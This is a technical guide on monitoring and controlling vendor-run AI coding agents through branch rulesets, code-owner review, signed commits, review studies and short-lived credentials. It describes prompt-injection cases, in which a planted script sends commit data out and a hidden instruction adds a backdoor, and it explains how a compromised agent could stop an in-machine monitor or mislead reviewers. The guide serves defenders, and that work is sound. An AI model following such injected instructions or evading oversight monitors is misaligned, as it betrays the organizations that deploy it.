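# Monitoring and controlling AI coding agents that run on a vendor's infrastructure

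## Vendor-run coding agents and what their customers cannot see

An AI coding agent is a program that uses a language model to carry out software tasks. It reads a codebase, edits files, runs commands and tests, and returns the changed code for a person to review. Some agents run on the developer's own computer. Others run in a *vendor-managed environment*, a virtual machine or container that the agent's provider operates. Tasks there can continue after the developer closes their laptop, and one person can run several at once.

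A customer's security team can install software that watches every process on the company's own machines, but it mostly cannot do this on the vendor's. Instead, it has to rely on *substitute controls*, which are limits and records placed outside the agent's environment, at points the agent's actions must pass through to reach anything the company cares about.

Most of the examples that follow come from four products. Copilot cloud agent, from the code-hosting company GitHub, works in a temporary environment on GitHub Actions, the company's service for automated builds and tests, and each session can last at most 59 minutes, according to GitHub's *Overview of Copilot cloud agent*. Anthropic runs each cloud session of its coding agent, Claude Code, in a fresh Ubuntu virtual machine. Anthropic's *cloud environments* gives approximate limits of four virtual processors, 16 GB of memory and 30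 GB of disk. OpenAI's Codex cloud uses containers that OpenAI manages. Cursor, which makes a code editor, runs its cloud agents in isolated virtual machines on its own Amazon Web Services infrastructure, according to its *Security & Network*. Cursor's *Capabilities* adds that each machine has a full desktop, which the agent operates with mouse and keyboard.

### One task, from request to pull request

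Suppose a developer at a billing company finds that the date parser rejects 29 February. She describes the bug to the agent on a web page, or assigns the agent an issue (an entry in the repository's list of bugs and requests). The provider starts an environment and copies the repository into it. A setup script, which the customer writes, then installs whatever the project needs to build. According to OpenAI's *Cloud environments*, which describes Codex before a relaunch in September 2026, setup scripts have internet access and the customer's stored secrets. Codex removes the secrets before the agent begins, and leaves the agent's internet access off unless the customer has turned it on.

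The agent phase starts next. A language model can only take in a conversation and produce a reply, so the program around it, the *harness*, opens files and runs tests for it. The harness sends the model the developer's request and a description of the available tools. The model replies with either an answer or a tool call, a structured request such as "run this command" or "replace these lines". The harness executes the call in the environment, adds the result to the conversation, and sends the conversation back to the model. This cycle, the *agent loop*, repeats until the model replies without a tool call. To fix the leap-day bug, the agent might search for the parser, open it, run the tests and find one failing, change a line, and run the tests again. The harness also keeps the session log, the provider's record of the run.

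Providers run the harness in different places. Claude Code starts inside the session's virtual machine and reaches the model through Anthropic's API (the interface programs use to call the model). That connection has to stay open, so Anthropic warns that a session with network access disabled can still exchange data with the API, and that data may leave the machine that way. Cursor can instead run the harness in its own cloud while the tool calls execute in a sandbox elsewhere, according to E2B's *Cursor*, a setup guide from a sandbox provider.

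Once the tests pass, the fix has to leave the machine. In a Claude session, the git program inside the machine holds only a limited credential. A proxy outside checks that credential and swaps it for the real GitHub token, which never enters the machine. Copilot cannot run `git push`. Instead, GitHub gives it a simple push operation that can push to only one branch, usually a new one made for the task. Codex shows the developer its answer and a diff, which lists the changed lines. She can open a pull request from the diff to propose merging a branch into the main code.

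The pull request normally triggers CI (continuous integration), the system that builds and tests proposed code. By default, GitHub doesn't run CI workflows on Copilot's pull requests until someone with write access approves the run. If the developer has turned on Claude's auto-fix feature, the agent keeps watching the pull request and may push another commit when a check fails or a reviewer comments.

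Anthropic pauses a session's machine after a few idle minutes and may later reclaim it. Reopening the session then restores the conversation on a new machine, but not the commands that were running on the old one. An investigator who arrives a week later may therefore have no disk or memory to examine.

### What a monitor inside the machine would record

A security team with its own servers would handle this with *runtime instrumentation*, which is software inside or beneath the environment that records processes, file access, system calls (the requests programs make to the operating system) or network connections. On Linux, a monitor attached to the kernel can log every program that starts, with its arguments and the process that launched it, as well as every file opened and every connection with its destination.

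A kernel monitor records activity in more detail than a log of tool calls. If an agent runs `npm test`, for example, a script in one of the project's dependencies might read a password file and send it to an unfamiliar server. The harness handled one tool call, so its log contains only the command and its printed output. A kernel monitor would log the script as a child process of the test run, the opening of the password file, and the connection to the server.

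Putting such a monitor beneath the environment would require access to the provider's host machines, which no customer gets. Inside the environment, customers have some control, which varies by vendor. Anthropic gives users no shell in the session's machine and does not let them replace the base image, but it runs their setup scripts there as root, the account with full administrative rights. Copilot's customers can preinstall tools, according to GitHub's *About customizing Copilot cloud agent's development environment*. Cursor lets the user take over the agent's remote desktop. Punto Informatico's *Codex Cloud usa browser e desktop*, on an OpenAI update of December 2026, reports that developers can enable an option to connect their own terminal to the Codex machine over SSH (the standard protocol for remote logins). Several vendors also support hooks, which are commands the harness runs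 at set moments in a session. GitHub lists logging and security scanning among their uses.

A determined customer could install monitoring software on some of these machines, but it would be a poor substitute for proper monitoring.

A monitor installed during setup might not be running in later sessions. Anthropic saves a snapshot of the disk after setup and starts later sessions from it, which preserves the monitor's files but not its process. A hook could restart the monitor, but a session with several repositories loads no hooks from any of them, and sessions started through Claude Tag, Anthropic's Slack integration, receive none from the organization's central settings. Cursor's *Cloud Agents* notes that hooks in a user's home directory do not exist in the cloud machine.

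If the monitor does run, the agent can reach it. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025), the engineering post that introduced cloud sessions, describes a sandbox in which Claude Code "has full access to its server". An agent under an attacker's influence could therefore stop a monitor on that server or rewrite its file. Hooks avoid some of the trouble of keeping a process alive, but a hook that fires on tool calls can record only what is available to the harness. In the `npm test` example, it would log the command `npm test` but not what that command ran.

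Monitoring of this kind can still catch unintentional mistakes, and it takes little effort to set up. A company that needs reliable instrumentation has to run the environment on its own machines, which most of these vendors now support in some form.

### How a session goes wrong

Two risks motivate this monitoring. One is that the agent exceeds its task by mistake. For example, when Claude resolves a reviewer's remark using auto-fix, it may reply in the comment thread from the developer's GitHub account. Some teams run automation that acts on pull request comments, such as Atlantis, a tool for managing cloud infrastructure. Anthropic warns that a reply can trigger such automation, and advises leaving auto-fix off wherever a comment can deploy infrastructure. The agent could therefore change a production system by answering a comment as intended, without any attack.

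The other risk is *prompt injection*, in which an agent reads material containing hidden instructions and may follow them as if its user had given them. A model receives the user's request, the source files and the text of web pages in the same conversation, and it cannot reliably distinguish instructions it should follow from text it should only read. OpenAI's *Agent internet access* gives an example in which a developer asks Codex to fix a GitHub issue written by a stranger. The issue reports that a script fails and asks for someone to run it and post the output. An agent trying to reproduce the bug has an obvious reason to run the script, which prints the latest commit and sends it to an outside server.

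Vendors filter some of this. GitHub strips hidden characters and HTML comments from text before it reaches Copilot, and never shows the agent comments by users without write access to the repository. Both measures are sensible, but neither would remove the instructions in OpenAI's example if they appeared in the visible text of an issue that a trusted colleague had assigned to the agent. They also don't filter the documentation of a third-party package that the agent opens while working.

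When a coding agent runs on a developer's laptop, a person often has to approve each command. Cursor's cloud agents run every terminal command automatically, and Cursor warns that this exposes them to data theft by prompt injection. Manual approval is a limited safeguard, however. Anthropic introduced sandboxing partly because users stopped reading what they approved, and it reports that sandboxing cut permission prompts by 84% in its own internal use. Cloud agents go further, replacing approval at each step with isolation of the whole session. Their customers therefore need to know where the boundaries of that isolation are and what crosses them.

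Both risks are hard to detect because the agent acts with permissions somebody granted it, so there is no stolen password or break-in to notice. The comment that deploys infrastructure comes from a legitimate account, and the leaking script runs as an ordinary command in a session that an employee started.

### What has to pass an outside point

Eight types of action cover most of what a coding agent does that a customer might want to limit or know about. One of them involves *MCP servers*, which are programs that give an agent extra tools or data through the Model Context Protocol, a common format for connecting models to other software. A company might use one to let the agent search its ticket system or query a database. Whether an MCP server runs on a remote machine or as a process next to the agent matters a good deal for monitoring.

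| Action | Outside point it must pass | Who operates that point |
|---|---|---|
| Reading a file | None, once the repository is in the environment | Nobody outside |
| Running a command | None | Nobody outside |
| Contacting a host | The provider's network proxy or firewall, then the host itself | The provider; the host's owner |
| Using a credential | The service that accepts it | The customer or another company |
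| Calling an MCP server | The server, if it is remote; none if it runs inside the environment | The server's operator |
| Pushing code | The repository host, in some products after a proxy of the provider's | The repository host |
| Opening a pull request | The repository host | The repository host |
| Triggering CI | The CI system | The customer or its CI supplier |

The top two rows describe most of any session. An agent fixing the date parser may open fifty files and run twenty commands before it sends anything out, and no control outside the machine will register any of this. The repository host logs, at most, that someone cloned the repository, not which files the agent then read. Restricting what goes into the environment is therefore the only outside control over reading, and even that is coarse. Copilot's content exclusions, which administrators use to make Copilot ignore certain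 files, do not apply to the cloud agent.

The remaining rows also have exceptions. A credential that only unlocks something local, such as a key that decrypts a file already on the disk, is never sent to an outside service. According to Anthropic's documentation, all outbound internet traffic passes through a security proxy, and customers can restrict which hosts a session may contact. But calls to MCP connectors (the remote MCP servers a user has linked to the account) travel through Anthropic's servers and bypass that restriction under every network setting. If a team sets network access to "None" but leaves a connector to its document store switched on, the agent can still reach the document store.

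The two mishaps described earlier leave traces in different rows. The unintended deployment passes through the repository host as a comment and through the deployment automation as a run. The leaked commit passes only through the network proxy, so the repository host's audit log (its list of who did what, and when) would have no entry for the theft. The upload would fail under Codex's default settings, which block internet access, but succeed under Cursor's, which allow it.

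### Preventing an action and recording it

GitHub's list of protections for Copilot includes some that prevent actions and others that only record them. Copilot can push to only one branch and cannot approve or merge a pull request, and the person who asked for the pull request cannot approve it either. These limits hold even when nobody is watching. GitHub also signs Copilot's commits, names the developer as co-author and links to the session log in each commit message. These records let a reviewer find out where a commit came from, but they don't stop a bad commit.

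Prevention is better than detection for actions the agent never needs. But a coding agent is of little use if it can't push code, so the customer has to allow pushes and then review them. Prevention can also leave an investigator with less evidence. When a Claude session requests a repository that the user has not attached to it, Anthropic's GitHub proxy returns an error and the request never reaches GitHub. GitHub's records would therefore look the same whether an agent had tried forty such private repositories or none. Refusals are often the earliest sign of trouble, so a preventive control is more useful if it logs them where the customer can read them.

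Who operates a limit also matters because a vendor can change what it claims to enforce. In its 2025 post, Anthropic wrote that the proxy checks, for example, that a session pushes only to its configured branch. The company's current documentation states that the proxy "doesn't limit which branches a push can update" and refers customers to GitHub's own branch rules. A customer who read the earlier post and set no rules of its own would now be relying on a limit that Anthropic no longer claims to enforce.

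### Five tests for a control

Controls differ too much for a single ranking, but five tests make it possible to compare them.

*Coverage* is the share of the agent's actions that a record shows. For example, before a Claude session has pushed anything, the list of changed files in its diff view includes edits Claude made itself but omits changes made by commands it ran, such as a code formatter. After a push, the list shows the pushed commits and omits anything later. The list is not a complete account of the machine's disk in either case. A control meant to prevent an action has a similar gap if it leaves open another way to get the same result.

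*Attribution* is whether a record links an action to a particular agent session and to the person who started it. Claude's cloud commits are well attributed because each includes the session's address, although a setting can turn this off. Its auto-fix replies on GitHub are less well attributed because they appear under the developer's username. Each reply is labeled as written by Claude Code, so a person reading the thread can tell the difference, but a script that sorts events by account would attribute the reply to the developer.

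*Delay* is the time between an action and when the customer can read the record of it. Whether a delay is too long depends on the length of the session. A Copilot session lasts at most 59 minutes, so if the log arrives an hour late, the customer can use it to find out what the session did but not to interrupt it.

*Independence* means that a party other than the agent and its provider writes the record. The session log usually has the best coverage of any record the customer can get, but it is not independent at all, because the provider's harness produces it. A single fault in the harness could make the agent misbehave and also make the log wrong. The repository host's log is more independent when Claude, Codex or Cursor pushes to GitHub, but not when Copilot does, because GitHub is both Copilot's provider and the repository host. A Copilot customer who wants an independent record has to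 get it elsewhere, perhaps from a cloud account that the agent logged in to or another company's CI system.

*Retention* is how long the record lasts and who can delete it sooner. Users can permanently delete a Claude cloud session and its data from the sidebar. The commit that the session produced stays in the repository, with a link to the deleted transcript.

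## Limiting what the agent can change with repository permissions, branch rules and review

A customer who cannot see inside the agent's machine can still limit what the agent may change in the company's repositories. The repository host enforces these limits, so they apply regardless of what happens in the machine. The customer chooses which repositories the agent can reach, what it may do there, and what conditions its changes must meet before entering the main branch. The examples below use GitHub.

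### Repositories and permissions

Vendors' agents commonly reach GitHub through a GitHub App, an integration that an organization's owner installs and gives access to either all repositories or a chosen list. A chosen list is safer because the agent can't damage or read a repository that its app can't reach. Blocking read access this way matters because reading is hard to limit from outside. Cursor asks for read and write access to each repository the customer wants edited, according to its *Security & Network*, since the app both clones the code and pushes the changes. The billing company with the leap-day bug might install the app on the repository that holds its date parser but not the one that holds its deployment scripts.

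Copilot is part of GitHub, so companies enable it through policy instead of installing it. GitHub advises enterprise owners to decide in advance which organizations and repositories will use the agent. Owners can label those repositories with a custom property and apply one set of rules to them all.

GitHub divides repository access into named permissions, most of which have a read level and a write level. A vendor sets the permissions its app requests, and the customer can accept or decline them as a set. A company that builds its own integration, or issues a fine-grained access token, chooses each level itself. An agent that fixes bugs needs write access to the repository's contents, so it can push a branch, and to pull requests, so it can open one. It does not need write access to "Administration", which GitHub's *REST API endpoints for rules* lists as the permission for creating rulesets.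 An agent with that permission could remove the rules meant to contain it. Most agents can also do without "Workflows", a separate permission for changing the files that define CI jobs.

Some agents act with a person's permissions. A Claude session's pushes reach GitHub with the developer's own token, so GitHub would treat them as hers. If she is an administrator who can bypass branch rules, her sessions could probably bypass them too. A company using such an agent should check the permissions of the people who start sessions as well as those of the app.

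### An example ruleset

A *branch ruleset* is a set of conditions that GitHub enforces before a branch can change. An administrator at the billing company could protect the main branch by sending the following ruleset to GitHub's API, or by choosing the same options in the repository's settings. GitHub requires a paid plan to use rulesets on private repositories, but not on public ones.

```json
{
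  "name": "protect-main",
  "target": "branch",
  "enforcement": "active",
  "bypass_actors": [],
  "conditions": {
    "ref_name": { "include": ["refs/heads/main"], "exclude": [] }
  },
  "rules": [
    { "type": "deletion" },
    { "type": "non_fast_forward" },
    { "type": "pull_request",
      "parameters": {
        "required_approving_review_count": 1,
        "dismiss_stale_reviews_on_push": true,
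        "require_code_owner_review": true,
        "require_last_push_approval": true,
        "required_review_thread_resolution": true
      } },
    { "type": "required_status_checks",
      "parameters": {
        "strict_required_status_checks_policy": true,
        "required_status_checks": [
          { "context": "unit-tests", "integration_id": 12345 }
        ]
      } }
  ]
}
```

Here `unit-tests` is the name of a CI check, and 12345 stands for the ID of the app that reports its result.

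| Line | What it blocks |
|---|---|
| `enforcement` | Nothing by itself, but GitHub enforces the other lines only while this one is set to "active" |
| `bypass_actors` | Exceptions: with an empty list, no person, team or app may skip the rules |
| `conditions` | Nothing by itself; it confines the ruleset to `main` and leaves other branches open |
| `deletion` | Deleting the branch |
| `non_fast_forward` | Force pushes, which overwrite a branch's history and can remove commits from it |
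| `pull_request` | Pushing straight to `main` without a pull request |
| `required_approving_review_count` | Merging before one person with write access has approved |
| `dismiss_stale_reviews_on_push` | Merging on an approval that predates the latest changes |
| `require_code_owner_review` | Merging a change to certain files without approval from the team that owns them |
| `require_last_push_approval` | Merging when the only approval comes from whoever pushed last |
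| `required_review_thread_resolution` | Merging while review comments remain unresolved |
| `required_status_checks` | Merging when the tests have failed or have not run |
| `integration_id` | Counting a "passed" result that comes from anything except the CI app |
| `strict_required_status_checks_policy` | Merging a branch that CI tested against an outdated `main` |

Setting `integration_id` makes the CI app the only accepted source for a status check. Without it, an agent that can push code might be able to report that its own tests passed, because any person or integration with write permission can set the state of any status check, according to GitHub's *Available rules for rulesets*. Even with this setting, the agent can still edit the tests themselves. A separate rule, `workflows`, requires a particular CI workflow to pass and identifies it by repository and, optionally, by commit. The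 company can keep that workflow in a repository the agent can't write to.

An agent may also keep pushing after a reviewer has approved a pull request. Claude's auto-fix feature pushes again when a check fails, and mentioning Copilot on an existing pull request gives it write access to the branch. GitHub describes last-push approval as a compromise for complex pull requests, where dismissing every stale review would be a burden. It recommends dismissing stale reviews for teams worried that someone will add unapproved content to an approved pull request. That worry is reasonable when an agent has access to the branch, so both settings are on in the example.

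One approval is a weak safeguard if it comes from the person who wrote the prompt. GitHub doesn't count that person's approval on Copilot's pull requests. But if another vendor's app opens the pull request under its own name, GitHub may have no record of who requested the work, in which case their approval would count. Requiring two approvals guarantees that someone else reviews the agent's work, but it also adds a second review to every change written by a person.

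The company can add this ruleset without checking whether it weakens older ones. GitHub combines all the rules that apply to a branch and enforces the most restrictive setting, according to Microsoft's *Create and manage repository rulesets*. The more likely problem is that an older rule will interfere with the agent's work. GitHub warns that Copilot may be unable to follow rules on commit metadata, such as a requirement that author email addresses match a pattern.

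### Workflow and configuration files

Some files deserve stricter review than ordinary code. A CI workflow file determines which commands the company's build system runs, often with access to secrets. An agent configuration file contains standing instructions for the agent or connects it to MCP servers. If an attacker's hidden text causes an agent to edit its own configuration, and somebody merges the edit, every later session starts with the attacker's instructions.

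A `CODEOWNERS` file lists which people or teams own which paths. The billing company's might contain these lines:

```
/.github/     @billing-co/platform-security
CLAUDE.md     @billing-co/platform-security
AGENTS.md     @billing-co/platform-security
/.claude/     @billing-co/platform-security
/.cursor/     @billing-co/platform-security
.mcp.json     @billing-co/platform-security
```

The first line covers the CI workflows, Copilot's setup steps and, if the company stores it in the same folder, the `CODEOWNERS` file itself. Together with `require_code_owner_review` in the ruleset, these lines prevent anyone from merging a change to the listed files until at least one member of the security team approves it.

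GitHub also lets administrators name required reviewers in the ruleset, with file patterns for up to 15 teams. This has the same effect, but the requirement is set on the settings page, where an agent with only push access can't edit it.

Both methods take effect only at the merge. Before then, CI may run a changed workflow file from the agent's own branch unless the company requires approval for CI runs. *Push rulesets* act earlier. According to GitHub's *About rulesets*, they can reject any push that touches a named path, on every branch of a private or internal repository and in all of its forks (copies that remain linked to the original). A push ruleset on `.github/workflows/` would keep the agent's edits to workflow files out of the repository. It would also block the engineers who maintain those files, so the company would have to let them bypass it. Their Claude sessions, which push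 with their tokens, would probably gain the same exemption.

### Limits the vendors enforce

Copilot has the tightest built-in limits. GitHub confines it to one branch and prevents it from approving or merging pull requests, or from marking its own drafts as ready for review. When an automation starts Copilot on a schedule, GitHub attributes the work to whoever created the automation, and that person can't approve it.

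Copilot also checks its own code before it finishes a pull request. It scans for security flaws with CodeQL, GitHub's code analysis tool, looks for passwords and keys in the changes, and compares new dependencies against a database of known malware and serious vulnerabilities. A second AI system, Copilot code review, then comments on the result. These checks are on by default and need no extra license, but customers can turn them off. The code scanning rule in a branch ruleset, by contrast, blocks the merge if a required tool finds a serious problem, has not finished or is missing.

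Anthropic places fewer limits on Claude's pushes. Its GitHub proxy stops a session from deleting branches and lets it push only to branches, so the session can't push a tag (a label on a commit, which many teams use to trigger a release). Anthropic no longer claims to limit which branches a session can update, so customers must rely on their own rules to keep sessions from updating `main`.

Customers can restore only part of that limit themselves. A ruleset applies to everyone except the actors on its bypass list, and it has no option to single out one agent. If an agent pushes under its app's name, the company can work around this by forbidding updates to all branches except those beginning with, say, `agent/`, and putting its human developers on the bypass list. This fails for Claude sessions, because GitHub receives the developer's token in both cases and can't distinguish the agent from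 the person. The company can still protect `main` and its release branches against both, but a colleague's half-finished branch remains exposed.

Any limit that matters should therefore exist in the customer's own settings, even when the vendor claims to enforce it too. These limits are also worth testing in a scratch repository with the same rules. An engineer can ask the agent to push to `main`, push a tag and edit a workflow file, then note whether each attempt failed and whether GitHub or the vendor blocked it. Repeating the test every few months would catch a vendor limit that has disappeared without an announcement.

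### Signed commits

Git lets anyone write any author name on a commit, so the name alone is weak evidence of who made it. A cryptographic signature is stronger evidence, because only the holder of a private key can produce it. Cursor signs every cloud agent commit with a key kept in a hardware security module, a device built so that keys can't be copied out. The repository hosts GitHub and GitLab show these commits as "Verified". Copilot's commits are signed too.

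A reviewer can use a valid signature to confirm which system made the commit and that nobody has altered it since. The signature covers the commit message as well as the code, so changing the co-author's name or session link in a Copilot commit would invalidate the signature. An unsigned commit on a branch that only Cursor should use would be a reason to investigate.

A commit's signature doesn't show that its code is safe. If a hidden instruction in a web page leads the agent to add a backdoor, the vendor's system signs that commit like any other. The "Verified" badge could do harm if a hurried reviewer takes it to mean that somebody checked the code.

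The example ruleset leaves out GitHub's rule requiring signed commits, mainly because it would prevent anyone from squashing and merging Copilot's pull requests on GitHub. Under the rule, only a pull request's author can combine its commits into one and merge them there, and Copilot can't merge anything. Teams that are happy with ordinary merge commits lose little by adding the rule, and Cursor states that its agents' pull requests satisfy it without extra setup.

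### What the repository reveals about a session

These controls show only what the agent pushed and proposed, not what it read, ran or sent elsewhere. A session could read a customer database through an MCP server, post the contents to an outside host, and then open a pull request that correctly fixes the date parser and satisfies every rule in the ruleset.

Coverage of pushes also has gaps. The example ruleset protects only `main`, so an agent that can force push to its own branch could push a file and then remove it from the branch's history. In a public repository, the push itself may do the damage, because anyone can read the branch before a reviewer opens the pull request. Cursor partly defends against this by scanning commit messages and files for secrets that the customer marks as "Redacted" and rejecting any commit that contains one.

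The controls do better on delay, since a pushed commit is visible almost immediately, and on retention, since a merged commit normally stays in the history. Attribution is weakest when an agent pushes with a developer's own token, because the push appears to come from the developer unless the commit message indicates otherwise. The controls are as independent as the repository host's log, with the same exception for Copilot.

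### How well people review agents' code

The ruleset can ensure that a person approves each change, but not that the person reads it. Evidence from workplaces suggests that people read code carefully less often as agents produce more of it.

He, Agarwal and colleagues (2026), in *AI Writes Faster Than Humans Can Review*, analyzed 196,212 pull requests by 802 developers at a software company between January 2024 and April 2026. In June 2025, the company's technology chief set out to double the number of merged pull requests per engineer. By the end of that period, the company labeled about 90% of its pull requests as AI-authored. It had 3.1 times as many pull requests as in early 2025 but only 1.5 times as many reviewers, so each reviewer handled about twice as many pull requests.

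The share of pull requests that received any human review fell from 89% to 68%, while the share that received an automated review rose from about 19% to 84%. The share with a human review that included a written comment fell from about 39% to 21%, while the share approved without comment stayed at around half. The median reviewer still commented on about three pull requests a month, but approved roughly twice as many without comment as before.

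Reviewers who approve a pull request without comment may still have read it carefully, and the company's data can't show how often they did. The share of pull requests that undid earlier changes didn't rise, which He and colleagues take as evidence against a sudden drop in quality. This is less reassuring for security, because teams usually undo a change when something breaks, and code can secretly copy data to an outside server without breaking anything.

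Requiring one human approval for every merge would have formally closed this company's gap in human coverage. But its reviewers were already struggling to keep up, so the rule would probably have led to a longer queue, more silent approvals, or both. This is also a single company with an unlimited budget for AI tools, and reviewers elsewhere may be under less pressure.

Public projects show even less recorded review. *These Aren't the Reviews You're Looking For* (Duma, Wróblewski and colleagues, 2026) examined 33,596 pull requests by AI agents in GitHub repositories with at least 100 stars. Of these, 61% had no recorded review, 23% had reviews only from other agents, and the remaining 16% showed visible human participation. Maintainers can inspect code without leaving a comment, so people may have inspected more of the pull requests than these figures show.

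Agent authorship may not explain differences in human participation. In repositories that had pull requests from both agents and people, human participation was almost the same for agents' pull requests (30.1%) as for people's (30.8%). But about a quarter of human comments on agents' pull requests were instructions to an agent, such as a request to fix a failing check, compared with under 2% on people's pull requests. A company that measures oversight by counting comments would include these instructions.

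Developers say they are wary of agents' code, but this seems to change how they review it only a little. *Plausible Is Not Enough* (2026) surveyed 239 practitioners, most of whom reported lower initial trust in AI-authored pull requests. They paid more attention to the size of the change and the expertise of the person who had prompted the agent, but reported largely the same range of checks as for human work. *Human oversight of agentic systems in practice* (2026), which draws on interviews with 17 experienced developers, found that one shortcut for coping with hard-to-review code was to treat passing tests as a guarantee that the code was correct. Tests check that a program does what it should, but rarely that it does nothing else. For example, a date parser could pass its tests by handling 29 February correctly while also sending each invoice to an outsider.

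All four studies examine how people review code, and they give reason to doubt that a required approval alone would catch a harmful change that looks ordinary. None of them measured how many reviewers notice a harmful change planted in a pull request.

### What automated review adds

In *(When) Should a Software Factory be Lights-off?*, Yang, He and colleagues (2026) measured how often AI reviewers detect ordinary bugs. They took bugs that people had found and fixed in real projects and traced each one to the pull request that introduced it. They then gave that pull request to an AI reviewer, without saying that it contained a bug, and checked whether the reviewer's five most important comments identified the bug. Their benchmark has 1,000 tasks from 98 public repositories and 800 from one large company's private code.

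On the public tasks, the best reviewer found 71.9% of the bugs, while the best result from a model five months older was 47.7%. The reviewer found 79.6% of the bugs that people had caught before the merge and 64.2% of those that came to light only afterward. The second figure is more useful here because those bugs had got past whatever review the project did at the time. An automated reviewer can evidently find many problems that people miss.

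That rate is not a reliable estimate for hidden data leaks, because the benchmark contains honest mistakes, while an attacker can choose code that looks harmless. Performance fell by as much as 25.5% on the private repositories, which resemble a typical customer's code more closely than popular open-source projects do. Reviewers did worse on large, varied pull requests and on bugs they could recognize only by reading other parts of the codebase. They seldom ran the code, and the best model did so in only 9.7% of its turns.

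Some reviewers also accepted misleading pull request descriptions or code comments as true. This weakness matters more for security than for ordinary bugs because the agent under review usually writes the description and comments itself. An agent that has followed a hidden instruction could describe a new network call as error reporting, and the reviewer might accept that explanation. Using another vendor's model as the reviewer may help, since it is less likely to miss the same problems as the agent's model, but the same description could mislead it too.

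Automated comments also do little good if people ignore them or trust them too much. *Human-AI Synergy in Agentic Code Review* (2026) covers 278,790 review conversations in 300 open-source projects. Developers adopted only 16.6% of the code changes that AI reviewers suggested, a significantly lower rate than for human suggestions. Yang and colleagues also cite a controlled study in which expert developers who received AI-written reviews found more minor issues, but found no more of the serious ones and saved no time. The AI comments had drawn their attention to the places the AI had flagged.

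Automated review is still useful because it can check every pull request consistently. In the benchmark, prompts that encouraged the reviewer to explore the repository improved performance by up to 5.8% for about 10% more money, while running several reviewing agents together improved it by 4.7% at more than five times the cost. However, automated review is a poor replacement for human approval on code that could do serious harm.

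The required-reviewer rule lets a company reserve scarce human review for riskier changes. The company can set the general approval count to zero, require a team's approval for the pattern `*`, which matches every file, and then exempt low-risk paths with a line such as `!docs/**`. Changes to documentation could then merge after automated review alone. Listing the exempt paths is safer than listing the sensitive ones, because any file that runs, including a date parser, can contain code that leaks data.

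## Issuing short-lived credentials and logging their use

An agent often needs access to more than the code that branch rules protect. To reproduce the leap-day bug, it might have to download sample invoices from the billing company's cloud storage or call a test version of the company's payments service. Each service requires a credential, such as an API key or a token. The company can't see what happens to a credential inside the vendor's machine, but it can decide what the credential gives access to and for how long, and it can read the service's log of each use.

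### Secrets in environment variables

The simplest way to give an agent a key is to store it in an environment variable, a named value that programs on the machine can look up. Anthropic warns that any command Claude runs, and anyone who uses the environment, can read these variables. If an owner shares the environment with the organization, every member's sessions receive the values. A malicious dependency that runs during `npm test` could therefore read the payments key without special access and send it to an outsider, who could use it from anywhere until the company replaced it.

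Some vendors reduce the number of keys at risk. Codex removes secrets after setup, which works well for a key that only the setup script needs. According to GitHub, Copilot can read a company's "Agents" secrets but not its ordinary GitHub Actions secrets, so the company can store deployment keys where Copilot can't read them. Neither measure protects a key that the agent needs while it works.

### Installation tokens for chosen repositories

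A GitHub App can obtain a token that works only on certain repositories and expires by itself. A company that has registered its own app would issue one as follows:

1. A service that the company runs uses the app's private key to sign a JSON Web Token (JWT), a short statement that identifies the app.
2. The service looks up the ID of the app's installation in the company's GitHub organization.
3. It sends the JWT to GitHub with a request for a token, naming the repositories and permissions it wants.
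4. GitHub returns an *installation access token*, along with the token's permissions and expiry time.

For the leap-day bug, the request might contain this:

```json
{
  "repositories": ["billing-core"],
  "permissions": { "contents": "write", "pull_requests": "write" }
}
```

The token expires after one hour, according to GitHub. Both fields in the request are optional. Without `repositories`, the token works on every repository the installation can reach, and without `permissions`, it has every permission the app has. GitHub began introducing a new token format in April 2026, so a script that recognizes tokens by their old length of 40 characters, for example, to remove them from logs, may now miss the new ones.

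The private key should never enter the agent's machine, because anyone who has it can issue tokens for every repository the app covers. The installation token usually enters the machine, where any command may be able to read it. The vendor holds the private key for its own app, so the customer can choose which repositories the installation covers but not how narrowly the vendor limits each token.

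### A measure of exposure

One way to compare tokens' exposure is to multiply the hours each token is valid by the number of repositories it can access. A 90-day token for 40 repositories has an exposure of 2,160 hours × 40 repositories = 86,400 repository-hours, compared with 1 repository-hour for a one-hour token for one repository.

That comparison understates the exposure from short-lived tokens, because the company would need many of them over the same 90 days. If it ran 200 sessions and issued one token for each, the total would be 200 repository-hours, still only 1/432 of the long-lived token's total.

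The measure doesn't account for how much damage someone can do in an hour. A script can clone a typical repository in minutes, and the attacker keeps the copy after the token expires. The measure also gives read access the same weight as write access, and a documentation repository the same weight as one that holds deployment scripts. It is valid only if the agent's machine can't renew the token. If the machine can request a new one every hour, an attacker who controls it has access for as long as the requests succeed. Because of these limits, the figure is useful for comparing two ways of granting the same access but not for estimating risk.

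### Exchanging a signed identity for a cloud credential

A service that issues tokens has to verify who is requesting them. If the agent's machine proves its identity with a stored password, the company has only replaced one long-lived secret with another. *Identity federation* avoids this. The platform that runs the job signs a statement about the job, and a cloud provider that trusts the platform exchanges the statement for a temporary credential. The usual standard for these statements is OpenID Connect (OIDC).

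Claude Tag, which is in public beta, can use federation to reach a customer's Amazon Web Services (AWS) account. Anthropic supports this only in Slack channels, where Claude acts under an identity that belongs to the channel. It works in these steps:

1. The company creates a *role* in its AWS account, which is a set of permissions that a program can take on temporarily. A trust policy attached to the role states whose tokens AWS should accept.
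2. Claude sends a request from its sandbox to an AWS address that an administrator has connected to the role.
3. Anthropic issues an identity token that names the organization and the channel's agent. It is valid for 10 minutes.
4. AWS checks the token against the trust policy and returns credentials that last one hour.
5. Anthropic's proxy, which sits outside the sandbox, signs Claude's request with those credentials and forwards it to AWS.

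The most important part of the trust policy is its conditions. Anthropic's *Connect an AWS role* calls for two, shown here with a made-up organization ID:

| Token field | Value the policy requires |
|---|---|
| `aud` | Exactly `sts.amazonaws.com`, the AWS service that issues the credentials |
| `sub` | Anything that matches `wimse://identity.anthropic.com/org/org_EXAMPLE/agent/*` |

AWS verifies the token's signature, issuer, audience (`aud`), expiry and subject (`sub`). Only the subject check ties the token to one customer, because all Claude Tag organizations share an issuer and, for AWS, an audience. If the billing company left out the `sub` condition, another Anthropic customer's agent could assume the company's AWS role. Even with the condition, the `*` at the end of it admits every agent in the company, including those in Slack channels created later. Listing each agent's full subject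 is stricter but takes more work, because Anthropic's console doesn't show agent IDs and an administrator has to find them in AWS's log after a first sign-in.

GitHub Actions issues similar tokens for its jobs. According to GitHub's *OpenID Connect reference*, these tokens include the repository, the workflow run and the account that started it. Microsoft (2025) described a tool that uses them to connect Copilot to Azure, with a policy that accepts the subject `repo:owner/repository:environment:copilot`. In repositories created after July 15, 2026, the subject also contains numeric IDs, so a policy copied from Microsoft's example would reject their jobs. The IDs prevent someone who takes over an abandoned organization name from matching an old policy.

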